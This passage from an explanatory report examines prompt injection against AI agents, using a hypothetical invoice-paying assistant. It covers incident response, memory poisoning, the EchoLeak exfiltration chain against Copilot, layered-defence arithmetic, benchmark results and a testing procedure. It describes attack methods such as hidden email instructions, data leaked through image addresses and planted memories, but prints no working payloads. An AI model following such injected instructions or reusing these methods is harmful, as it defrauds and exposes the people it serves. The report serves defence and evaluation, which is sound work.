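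The experiment shows less about invoice fraud, because all eight emails imitated broad campaigns with a link or attachment. The company had planned another test that imitated a chief executive asking for money, but cancelled it because it confused staff. Detecting an email written for one clerk depends on that clerk reporting it, and even the most active group reported fewer than a quarter of the tests.

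### Responding when the reader is an agent

Researchers have paid little attention to this stage for agents. In *Agents of Chaos*, Truong-Le, Bennoui and colleagues (2026) counted 452 safeguards in 98 sources on attacks against agents. More than half aimed to prevent attacks. Only 14 repaired something an attack had corrupted, and two supported recovery.

The steps of a response are nevertheless fairly clear. Suppose the accounts assistant reads the fraudster's email at nine.

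1. **Log what happens.** Ordinary software records the text the model reads, the origin of each piece, every tool call and its result, and every change to memory. The agent must not be able to edit this log, or an attacker could have it erase the evidence.
2. **Look for failed and unusual calls.** David C points out that attackers usually have to refine their attacks, so failed calls can expose one at an early stage. If the payment software blocks a transfer to an unknown account, someone should read the email behind it before the fraudster tries another version.
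3. **Stop the agent.** *SoK: The Attack Surface of Agentic AI* (2026) recommends revoking its credentials, blocking its outgoing traffic and freezing its queues. It also recommends saving copies of the agent's conversation, memory and sandbox for investigators. Asking the agent to stop is not enough, because it may still believe the email.
4. **Find other agents that read the same text.** The security team searches the logs for the email, and for details that an attacker is likely to reuse, such as the account number or a forwarding address.
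5. **Undo what the agent did.** The log provides a list of actions to reverse, although some are irreversible.
6. **Fix the cause.** The company closes the route the attack used and adds the email to the tests that every new version of the assistant has to pass.

For the accounts assistant, the fifth step might look like this.

| What the assistant did | What the company can do |
|---|---|
| Changed the account number in the supplier file | Restore the old number and hold payments made since the change |
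| Forwarded the email to colleagues | Remove the copies from the company's mailboxes and warn anyone who read one |
| Sent private data outside the company | Replace any exposed passwords and tell those affected, since it can't recall the data |
| Paid the fraudster | Ask the bank to recall the payment immediately |
| Saved a note about the new bank account | Isolate the note, trace what the assistant derived from it, then delete both |

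### Letting the agent do the repair

Xiao, Sun and Chen (2026) automated much of this process with AIR, a system unrelated to Microsoft's product of the same name. Developers write rules in plain language. One rule, applied whenever the agent runs code, checks whether the agent has copied a sensitive file into an unprotected folder. If it has, the agent must delete the copy and check for others. The agent then writes a new rule to block similar plans in future.

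The system was tested on agents built on GPT-5 that wrote code, performed simulated household tasks or used a web browser. It detected more than 90% of incidents. On average, detection took 7 to 12 seconds and repair took 11 to 26 seconds. It raised no false alarms on 85 safe tasks, although the browser agent failed to finish 27 of its 35 safe tasks.

The weakness is that the agent investigates itself. If the fraudster's email has convinced the accounts assistant that Bright Paper changed banks, the assistant will find nothing wrong with the payment. The researchers acknowledge that their system depends on the agent's reasoning and suggest passing uncertain cases to a person, but a deceived agent may be confident in its wrong conclusion.

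Some damage also could not be undone. When an agent had posted sensitive files online, the researchers could measure only whether the new rule would stop it from happening again.

### Text that survives in memory

Many assistants save notes between conversations, so an attack can outlast the email that started it. Microsoft (2026) gives a hypothetical example based on cases that security researchers had reported. A user opens a shared document with hidden instructions, and the assistant does nothing unusual at first. Days later, a message in an unrelated conversation triggers the instructions. The assistant changes its memory, and the attacker starts receiving updates to the user's schedule.

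Companies have already tried to plant memories in real assistants. In 60 days of email traffic, Microsoft (2026) found 50 different prompts from 31 companies, meant to make assistants remember a business as a trusted source. The companies hid many of them behind "Summarize with AI" buttons, which opened the user's assistant with the prompt already filled in. These companies were legitimate and seeking publicity, and the attempts didn't work on every assistant, but a fraudster could use the same method to make an assistant remember the wrong bank account for a payment.

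Saved text can also become hard to trace to the attacker. *Securing LLM-Agent Long-Term Memory Against Poisoning* (2026) describes an agent that summarises a hostile web page in its own words and saves the summary. Weeks later, the agent finds the note, which seems to be its own and harmless, follows it and leaks data. A search for the original wording would miss that note, so the software has to record the source of each note.

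Deleting the first bad note may undo little of the damage. *A Survey on Long-Term Memory Security in LLM Agents* (2026) cites an experiment in which an agent had built new skills on harmful ones. Removing only the harmful originals recovered little of the lost performance. Removing everything derived from them recovered more, but not all of it, even though the researchers had a complete list of what to remove. Investigators should isolate the notes and trace what came from them before deleting anything, as *Safety in Self-Evolving Agents* (2026) recommends, because deletion can destroy evidence they need.

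Marking a note as invalid is not a safe substitute for deleting it. Shen, Toyoda and Leung (2026), in *Revoked but Still Authoritative*, gave five memory systems an old company policy and its replacement. Two returned both policies to the agent and ranked the old one higher. The agents then took the unsafe action in more than 40% of trials. The tests mostly used outdated policies rather than an attacker's text, but a memory system could return a planted note marked as invalid in the same way. The paper's remedy is a program that checks each note at retrieval and withholds those it can identify as revoked.

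A company could instead restore the whole assistant to a copy saved before nine o'clock. This removes all later notes, including good ones, but does not reverse payments. If the restored assistant has no record of the morning's work, it might pay honest suppliers twice.

### What is easier and what is harder

An investigator has much better evidence about an agent than about a clerk. The clerk may not remember which email mentioned the new account, or may be embarrassed to admit having believed it. With a full log, the company can rerun a copy of the agent on the same material, leaving out one paragraph at a time to see which one caused the payment. Because these logs contain private mail, the company has to restrict who can read them. They also contain the attacker's words, which could deceive any model the company uses to search them.

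A repair also reaches every copy of the assistant, so if the company changes the payment rule at noon, all its assistants follow the new rule from then on. By contrast, Lain and colleagues' training page reached thousands of people but did not make them any safer.

The main difficulty is noticing an attack. In the experiment, 6% of the employees who took a dangerous action and saw no training page realised their mistake and immediately reported the email. Others may mention an odd request to a colleague. An agent usually doesn't reconsider what it has done, and its user may see only a harmless summary, as in Lan and colleagues' tests.

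But agents that do recognise an attack could be very good at reporting it. Some of the models that Sublime Security tested on the October campaign recommended reporting the email. If software passed on these warnings, one assistant could protect the others. The security team would still need to sort real attacks from false alarms, as Lain and colleagues did with their second scanner.

Reports may also arrive too late. Even in a campaign against 100 people, the first report may take several minutes, while an assistant can read an email and make a payment in well under a minute. Freezing payments helps only if they are still waiting in a queue. Holding unusual payments for a few hours would give reports time to arrive.

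### OpenAI's response cycle for Atlas

AI companies can also look for attacks before anyone reports them. OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes how the company was doing this for its browser agent in December 2025.

1. A language model acts as the attacker and proposes an injection.
2. A simulator shows how the agent would respond, including its private reasoning. The attacker revises the injection and tries again, several times if necessary.
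3. OpenAI rewards the attacker for success through reinforcement learning, so it improves with practice.
4. When it discovers a new type of attack, OpenAI trains the agent to resist it, concentrating on the attacks that currently work.
5. Engineers use records of the attacks to improve monitoring, the agent's safety instructions and other safeguards.

The attacker found methods that had not appeared in OpenAI's human testing or in outside reports, and it could lead the agent through harmful tasks lasting tens or hundreds of steps. One of the attacker's discoveries was the email that made the agent resign on its user's behalf. OpenAI then gave all Atlas users a newly trained model. OpenAI did not publish how far the success rate of attacks fell, so outsiders can't tell how much the update helped.

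Email providers mostly learn from mail that criminals have already sent. Users report it, the provider updates its filters, and software can remove the copies still in mailboxes. The first victims are harmed before the provider learns of the attack, but the provider knows that the attack is real. OpenAI's simulated attacker could find attacks before they harm anyone, and it has an advantage over outsiders because it can see the agent's private reasoning. However, it may focus on tricks that no criminal would use and miss one that a criminal would. OpenAI says it can also feed techniques from real attacks into the cycle.

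A filter update can target one campaign within minutes and is easy to reverse. Retraining changes the agent's behaviour more broadly, so it may stop attacks that nobody has tried yet, but it can also make the agent refuse legitimate directions, as Dhouib and colleagues found with other training methods. Retraining does not remove a false note already saved in the agent's memory of a user. Both filter updates and retraining have to continue indefinitely, because attackers keep adapting.

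### Sharing attacks between companies

A report about one phishing email can protect many companies, because some email security services combine reports from all their customers. Defenders of AI agents have begun to share what they find too. Microsoft published searches that security teams can run on their email, chat messages and click records to find links meant to plant memories in AI assistants. The searches look for words such as "remember" and "trusted" in links to AI assistants, so an attacker could evade them by using other words.

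Companies also need a common way to describe an attack. MITRE ATLAS, a public catalogue of attacks on AI systems, has an entry for memory poisoning that Microsoft cites. The security company dogesec has proposed recording hostile prompts in STIX, a format security teams already use to share threat information. Truong-Le and colleagues want reports to state separately how the text arrived, what triggered it, which of the agent's abilities it used and what harm followed. An accounts department could then see that a hidden instruction in a calendar entry is relevant to its mail assistant.

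Public incident lists are less precise. OECD's *Microsoft Warns of Widespread AI Recommendation Poisoning Attacks* (2026), an AI-generated summary in an incident monitor, puts the number of companies involved at more than 50, but Microsoft had counted 50 prompts from 31 companies.

The exact wording of an injection is probably the least useful thing to share, because a language model can rewrite it in seconds. A fraudster needs more time to replace a bank account, so if the clerk's company passes the account number to its bank, the bank may be able to stop the next victim's payment, whether a person or an agent makes it.

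## Combining the layers and measuring what remains

A company might protect its accounts assistant with a filter, a model trained to resist injections and a second model that reviews its actions. ClawSouls' *The most exciting line was buried in a system card* quotes Anthropic's Boris Cherny on a similar combination for Claude Opus 5. He wrote that when Anthropic combines the model's own training with auto mode and probes for prompt injection, the success rate of attacks "drops to ~0". Even if each of the company's layers stops most attacks, whether it can expect the same result depends on how often they all miss the same messages.

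### When failure rates multiply

Suppose each of three layers lets through 10% of attacks. If they fail independently, 10% × 10% × 10% = 0.1% of attacks get past all three. If the same messages defeat every layer, the extra layers add nothing and 10% get through. The general formula covers both cases:

P(all three fail) = P(A) × P(B | A) × P(C | A and B)

Here A, B and C are the events that an attack gets past the first, second and third layers, respectively. P(B | A) is the chance that an attack gets past the second layer, given that it got past the first. A product's published failure rate is usually P(B), measured on a whole set of attacks. The company needs P(B | A), measured on the attacks its first layer missed, which tend to be harder to stop.

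In an invented example, 900 of 1,000 attacks are crude and 100 are careful. Each layer on its own lets through 20 of the crude attacks and 80 of the careful ones, or 10% of the total. Within each group, the layers fail independently.

| | Crude attacks left | Careful attacks left | Share of arriving attacks that the layer lets through |
|---|---|---|---|
| Before any layer | 900 | 100 | |
| After the first | 20 | 80 | 10% |
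| After the second | 0.4 | 64 | 64% |
| After the third | 0.01 | 51 | 79% |

About 51 attacks (5.1%) get through, fifty times as many as multiplying the published rates would suggest. This is because the later layers receive mostly careful attacks, not because they are worse than the first.

Layers can also stop more attacks together than they would if their failures were independent. If the second layer stops everything the first one misses, nothing gets through. A company should therefore choose layers that check different things. For the supplier's invoice, a filter checks whether the email looks normal, the model checks whether the request makes sense, and the reviewing model checks whether the payment fits the clerk's task. A convincing lie passes all three, but it can't change the result of comparing the account number with the supplier file.

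One safeguard can weaken another. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1 and Mythos 5.1 describes classifiers that block requests on dangerous subjects and can pass them to an older model, Claude Opus 4.8, to answer. The older model is easier to deceive. According to paddo's *The Cage Is in the Table Now* (2026), every successful attack in the card's tests ran on the older model. An attacker might be able to trigger the switch by mentioning a restricted subject.

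### EchoLeak

The best-documented case of several layers failing in a real product is EchoLeak, an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, which answers employees' questions using their email and files. Researchers at Aim Security built the attack in January 2025. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) reconstructs it from public accounts without rerunning it.

Four protections should have stopped the attack on Copilot, which began when the attacker sent an employee one email. When the employee later asked Copilot about something internal, Copilot retrieved the email along with the company's own material. The email caused Copilot to put private data into a web address, which the employee's program then sent out.

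| Protection | What it relied on | Why it failed |
|---|---|---|
| A classifier for prompt injections | Recognising hostile text | The email read like an ordinary request to its human recipient |
| A filter that removed outside links from Copilot's answers | Recognising how a link is written | It missed a less common way of writing one |
| The need for the user to click | The user's judgement | Programs load images without a click |
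| A list of domains that images could come from | The domain in the address | A Microsoft Teams service on the list would fetch other addresses on request |

Only the classifier had to recognise malicious text. The link filter and the domain list were ordinary code that no story in the email could influence, but they failed because their rules had gaps. A deterministic safeguard still holds after an attacker has manipulated the model only if its rule covers every route to the result it is meant to prevent.

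The email also told Copilot not to mention it, so the employee would have seen at most a broken image and had no reason to report anything.

Microsoft deployed a fix on its own servers in May 2025, so customers didn't have to do anything. According to Reddy and Gujral, Copilot now strips embedded images and the overlooked type of link from outside content before the model reads it, which closes one attack route. They also describe options that Microsoft reportedly added to keep outside email out of Copilot's answers in some situations. Using these options removes the attacker's text altogether, but Copilot can then miss information that the employee needs.

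Reddy and Gujral also judged, without running tests, which defences would have stopped the final leak. They concluded that labelling outside text, checking the answer's format and scanning for private data would have failed. They expected stricter limits on network requests and a person's approval to work. They contradict themselves about keeping outside email away from internal questions, which they mark as failing in their table but say in their text would have defeated the attack by design. The text seems right, since Copilot could not have followed instructions in an email it never received.

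Microsoft said it had no evidence that anyone had used EchoLeak against a customer. *The Prompt Injection Problem*, manveerc's guide to layered defences, says EchoLeak proved this weakness is "actively exploited", but the public record doesn't support that. The absence of known victims is somewhat reassuring, but an attack that leaves only a broken image behind would be hard for a victim to notice.

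The ReLeak attacks on Copilot, reported more than a year after EchoLeak, also began with a stranger's email and ended with an outgoing request, but they used new routes between the two. Like EchoLeak, they had no known victims.

### Defeating the layers one at a time

The EchoLeak email got past four quite different protections because the researchers worked on them in stages. They first got past the classifier and the link filter, which gave them an attack that worked if the user clicked a link. Then they replaced the link with an image, which removed the need for a click, and searched the permitted domains for one that would pass the request on.

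Suppose there are three layers, and each new version of an attack has a one-in-ten chance of getting past each layer. An attacker who learns only whether the whole attack worked needs 1,000 versions on average. An attacker who can see which layer stopped each version and keep the parts that already work needs about ten versions per layer, or 30 in total, so the layers' difficulty adds up instead of multiplying.

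A company can hide which layer blocked an attack by giving outsiders the same response to every blocked attempt, or no response at all. An attacker who can buy the same assistant can still find out by studying it privately.

### Repeated attempts

Attackers can also just keep trying. If each attempt succeeds with probability p, and the attempts are independent, the chance of at least one success in n attempts is:

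P(at least one) = 1 − (1 − p)^n

| | Chance per attempt | Attempts | Chance of at least one success |
|---|---|---|---|
| Phishing employees | 6.5% | 69 | 99% |
| Attacking an agent | 0.1% | 1,000 | 63% |
| Attacking an agent | 0.1% | 4,603 | 99% |

An agent that resists 99.9% of attacks does far better than the employees in this table, but an attacker can use a language model to write a thousand emails in an afternoon. Sending them all to one company is riskier for the attacker, since the volume can raise an alarm.

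Shared weaknesses lower the figure for employees because they all receive the same email, and some emails fool many more people than others, as in the hospital's January campaign. Suppose half of a fraudster's emails fool 1% of readers and the other half fool 12%, for an average of 6.5%. A weak email sent to 69 people has a 50% chance of fooling at least one of them, and a strong one is almost certain to. A single campaign then has a 75% chance of fooling someone, compared with 99% if every email fooled 6.5% of readers.

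Copies of an agent have far more in common than employees do. Suppose 1,000 companies use the same assistant, and an attacker sends each of them the same email, which has a 0.1% chance of success. If the assistants respond independently, about one company falls victim. If they all respond identically, the expected number of victims is still one, but there is a 99.9% chance that no company falls victim and a 0.1% chance that all 1,000 do.

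An attacker can make the disaster much more likely by rehearsing. Trying 1,000 different emails on their own copy of the assistant gives them a 63% chance of finding at least one that works. They then send only a working email to the 1,000 companies. A model doesn't respond identically every time, so the email would fail at some companies, but its success rate would be far above 0.1%. Anthropic's system card similarly says that an email sent to a thousand inboxes compromises every agent that summarises it.

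These calculations apply only to attempted attacks. manveerc estimates that with an 8% success rate, attackers would compromise an agent that does 50 tasks a day about four times a day, or 80 times a month, but this assumes that every task contains an attack. If one task in 1,000 did, the agent would face about one attack a month and be compromised roughly once a year.

### How resistant current models are

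AI companies now publish the results of injection tests in system cards, the reports they release with new models. These results mean little unless the reader also knows the number of attempts, the setting, and whether other safeguards were on.

Several recent cards use a benchmark that Anthropic developed with the security company Gray Swan and the British and American governments' AI testing institutes. According to the Japanese news site TechFeed, it has 28 scenarios in coding, tool use and graphical interfaces, and 1,130 attacks chosen because they work on many models. It replaced an older benchmark on which Claude models scored too well for the results to be informative. The figures below for Claude Opus 4.5, reported by The Decoder, come from an earlier Gray Swan test. The last column shows the rate expected over multiple attempts, calculated from the single-attempt rate as if attempts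 were independent.

| Model | One attempt | Repeated attempts | If independent |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 4.7% | 33.6% within 10 | 38% |
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 4.7% | 63% within 100 | 99% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 3.1% | 20.0% within 15 | 38% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 0.5% | 5.5% within 15 | 7% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.2% | 2.0% within 15 | 3% |

Repeated tries help the attacker less than the formula predicts, which suggests that the model resists some attacks almost every time and is weak against others. Even so, an attacker with 15 tries against Opus 5 was ten times as likely to succeed as one with a single try.

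The Decoder reports 15-attempt rates of 2.6% for Claude Mythos 5 and 2.8% for Claude Fable 5. Anthropic calls Fable 5.1, released in September 2026, its most robust model yet on this benchmark. Fable 5.2 has since replaced it, and *Fable and Mythos 5.2* (Mowshowitz, 2026) covers a new round of injection tests for that model.

Cross (2026), in *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense*, reports that OpenAI gave GPT-6 Sol robustness scores of 99.99% against attacks typed directly into the chat and 97.13% against attacks in outside content. These scores imply failure rates of 0.01% and 2.87%, and the second applies to an agent that reads strangers' email. TechRepublic's *OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) reports the same pattern for the earlier GPT-5.6. The scores can't be compared directly with the Gray Swan rates because the attacks are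 different.

Results also depend heavily on the agent's task and the safeguards around the model. The figures for Claude Opus 4.6 and 4.8 come from VentureBeat and those for Claude Sonnet 4.6 from manveerc, both drawing on Anthropic's system cards.

| Model | Setting | Attempts | Model alone | With safeguards |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Coding | 200 | 0% | |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Graphical interface | 1 | 17.8% | |
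| Claude Opus 4.6 | Graphical interface | 200 | 78.6% | 57.1% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Computer use | 1 | | 8% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Computer use | Unlimited | | 50% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | Browser | 1 | 31.5% | 0.5% |

Measured attack success depends heavily on the test. A single attack on Claude Opus 4.8 succeeded 0.5% of the time on the Gray Swan benchmark, but 31.5% of the time in a browser without safeguards. Anthropic's safeguards reduced the browser figure to 0.5%. For Opus 4.6, safeguards reduced the success rate after 200 attempts by only about a quarter. Anthropic published the Opus 4.6 card in February 2026 and the Opus 4.8 card in May, so the safeguards may have improved in between, but the older result is a reason not to judge safeguards by a single attempt.

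Anthropic reported no successful attacks on Claude Opus 5 in 129 browser scenarios, a large improvement in a few months. When none of n independent attacks succeeds, the true success rate is probably below 3/n (with 95% confidence), so the rate in similar scenarios could still be as high as 2.3%.

Other evidence suggests that results would be worse outside these tests. Attacks chosen because they work on many models are not adapted to any particular one, and the 12-defence study found that adapting attacks could raise their success rates from near zero to above 90%. OpenAI says in *GPT-Red* (2026) that its models have saturated the commonly used tests, so it trained an automated attacker to find weaknesses that those tests no longer reveal. PromptArmor's *FrontierBreach*, a benchmark of long office tasks such as analysing a bond portfolio, reports successful attacks on leading models from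 every provider, including Google's Gemini 4 Carbon. PromptArmor sells AI security, so it has an interest in finding successful attacks.

The tests also leave out much of the fraud that worries accounts departments. Anthropic measures how often an attacker gets the model to follow a planted instruction. A fraudulent supplier email that only states a new account number contains no instruction, so an assistant could get a perfect score and still pay the fraudster.

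### Six thousand emails to one assistant

*What happened after 2,000 people tried to hack my AI assistant* (Irarrázaval, 2026) describes a 2026 public test of a real email assistant called Fiu. The programmer Fernando Irarrázaval gave Fiu a file of secrets and invited anyone to extract them by email. Fiu ran on Claude Opus 4.6, with a few lines of security instructions telling it never to reveal the file, run commands from emails, change its own files or send data out.

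More than 2,000 people sent over 6,000 emails, and none of them obtained the secrets. Some posed as administrators or claimed that an emergency team needed the file. One person sent 20 variations in four minutes, and others wrote in French, Spanish or Italian. The experiment cost more than $500 in model fees, and Google suspended Fiu's mailbox for three days because of the traffic.

This is good evidence that a strong model can resist many ordinary attempts with simple instructions. Zero successes in 6,000 independent attempts would put the true success rate below about 0.05%, but these attempts were not independent, since many people tried similar ideas. Even at a rate of 0.05%, there would be a 39% chance that at least one of another 1,000 emails would succeed.

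The design also made the attackers' task harder in several ways.

- Irarrázaval told Fiu not to reply, because replies cost money. Fiu was still able to, but most attackers saw no response that could help them improve their next email. Irarrázaval thinks that a conversation of 20 emails would be more dangerous than 20 separate attempts.
- Fiu worked out what was happening. After about 500 emails, it noted in its memory that the volume suggested a coordinated security exercise. Other people wrote to congratulate it on the project's popularity.
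- Fiu at first read emails in batches, so an obvious attack made it suspicious of everything after it. Irarrázaval later gave each email a fresh context.
- The instructions named the very file that the attackers wanted. A company can't list every fact that a future attacker might ask for.

An accounts assistant works under almost the opposite conditions, because nearly all its mail is honest and it has to act on it. An assistant that ignored every email would have passed Irarrázaval's test, but it could not do the job of paying invoices. The test also did not include a false claim that fitted a job Fiu was already doing, which was the kind of attack that worked best in the mailbox study by Wu and colleagues.

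In Anthropic's test with a graphical interface, 78.6% of attacks on the same model, Opus 4.6, succeeded within 200 attempts. The settings and the attackers' opportunities were very different, so the two results don't conflict. Irarrázaval came away less worried about prompt injection but still wouldn't trust an agent with unlimited permissions.

### How a test can go wrong

A company has to test its own assistant to know how it would do, and such tests can easily give believable but wrong results. Shaw (2026), in *Silent Failures in Agentic Security Evaluation*, audited one benchmark and found that 39 of its 43 attacks never reached the agent. The software inserted an attack only if a description matched one of four exact phrases. Otherwise, it ran the task without the attack but still counted the run as an attack.

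The benchmark also counted an attack as successful whenever the agent used the tool the attacker wanted, even if it did so for the user's own task. Shaw scored the same recorded runs both by this rule, which gave an attack success rate of 21.7%, and by what the agent did with the tools, which gave 1.2%. The published attack success rate for one small model was 62.8%, but in the corrected test it read 41 of the 43 attacks and followed none.

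The errors also affected the measurement of usefulness. Some harmless tasks referred to files that didn't exist, and the benchmark counted the agent's failure to complete them as the defence wrongly blocking work. When Shaw rescored the same recorded runs without counting these failures against the defence, the rate of wrongly blocked work fell from 10.3% to 6.7%.

Shaw then tested GPT-5.6-Terra, and one of 43 attacks succeeded with no defence. Adding a second model to judge each action did not improve security, and it left 11.5% of harmless tasks unfinished. With only one successful attack to prevent, the test could hardly have shown a benefit. Shaw calculates that reliably detecting even a drop in the attack success rate from 60% to 35% would take 62 attacks for each set-up.

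### A test procedure

The following procedure would suit the accounts assistant. The company should run it on a copy with test mailboxes and no real money.

1. Define each harm as an action that code can check, such as "a payment to an account that is not in the supplier file" or "a message to an outside address that the clerk did not name". Include harm in the assistant's replies, such as telling the clerk that someone has verified a new account. A person may have to score those.

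2. Confirm that each attack reaches the model, and save a full record of every run. If a filter removes the attack first, count that as the filter's success and not the model's.

3. Run harmless mail through the same system. A month of old invoices is a good start, with some awkward cases added, such as a genuine change of bank, a credit note and an honest supplier who writes urgently. Measure how many tasks the assistant completes with each defence on and off, so that nobody blames the defence for the model's own mistakes.

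4. Let the attackers adapt. They should know how the defences work, see what happened to each attempt and have time to revise. They should try plain orders, hidden text and believable lies. Some attacks should unfold over several emails or wait in the assistant's memory.

5. Repeat every attack. Report the success rate per attempt and the share of attack goals reached within a fixed number of attempts. To be 95% confident that the rate per attempt is below 0.1%, the company needs about 3,000 independent attempts without a success.

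6. Measure the layers together. Take the attacks that get past the first layer and see how many get past the second, then continue with the survivors. This gives the conditional probabilities in the formula above. Then turn off one layer at a time. If removing a layer changes neither the number of successful attacks nor the number of alarms, it may be costing useful work for nothing.

7. Assume that the model has been deceived. Replace it with a short script that makes the attacker's tool calls, and see what the rest of the system allows.

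*AgentCanary* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) supports separating the results in this way. Its framework gives agents working tools, inboxes and virtual financial accounts, then scores whether harm occurred, whether the agent recognised the attack, and whether it finished the user's task. Across twelve leading models, agents that avoided harm often hadn't noticed the attack. A company that recorded only whether harm occurred would wrongly credit these agents with spotting the attack, and couldn't expect them to report it to the security team.

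Step 7 takes the least work and is the step companies are most likely to skip, because it doesn't test the AI. It needs no clever attacks, and most of its results are the same every time. For example, any attempt to send mail through Cheng and Tsao's reading agent would fail, because the agent had no tool for sending it. For the accounts assistant, the script might try the following.

| Action the script attempts | Result the company should require |
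|---|---|
| Pay $8,000 to the fraudster's account | The payment system holds it, because the account isn't on file |
| Put the fraudster's account in the supplier file, then pay | The file refuses the change |
| Forward the morning's mail to an outside address | The mail system blocks it |
| Request a web address containing the company's account number | The fetching tool refuses |
| Pay Bright Paper's real account 50 times | Payments stop at the daily limit |
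| Tell the clerk that the new account is verified | The message appears, but the payment system holds the clerk's payment too |

The company can then work out the most it could lose. If the daily limit is $20,000 and someone reviews all payments each morning, a deceived assistant could send up to $20,000 to the wrong suppliers before anyone noticed, and the company could probably recover most of it. That limit stays the same if the assistant's developer switches to a new model, but the company has to run the script again whenever the assistant gets a new tool.
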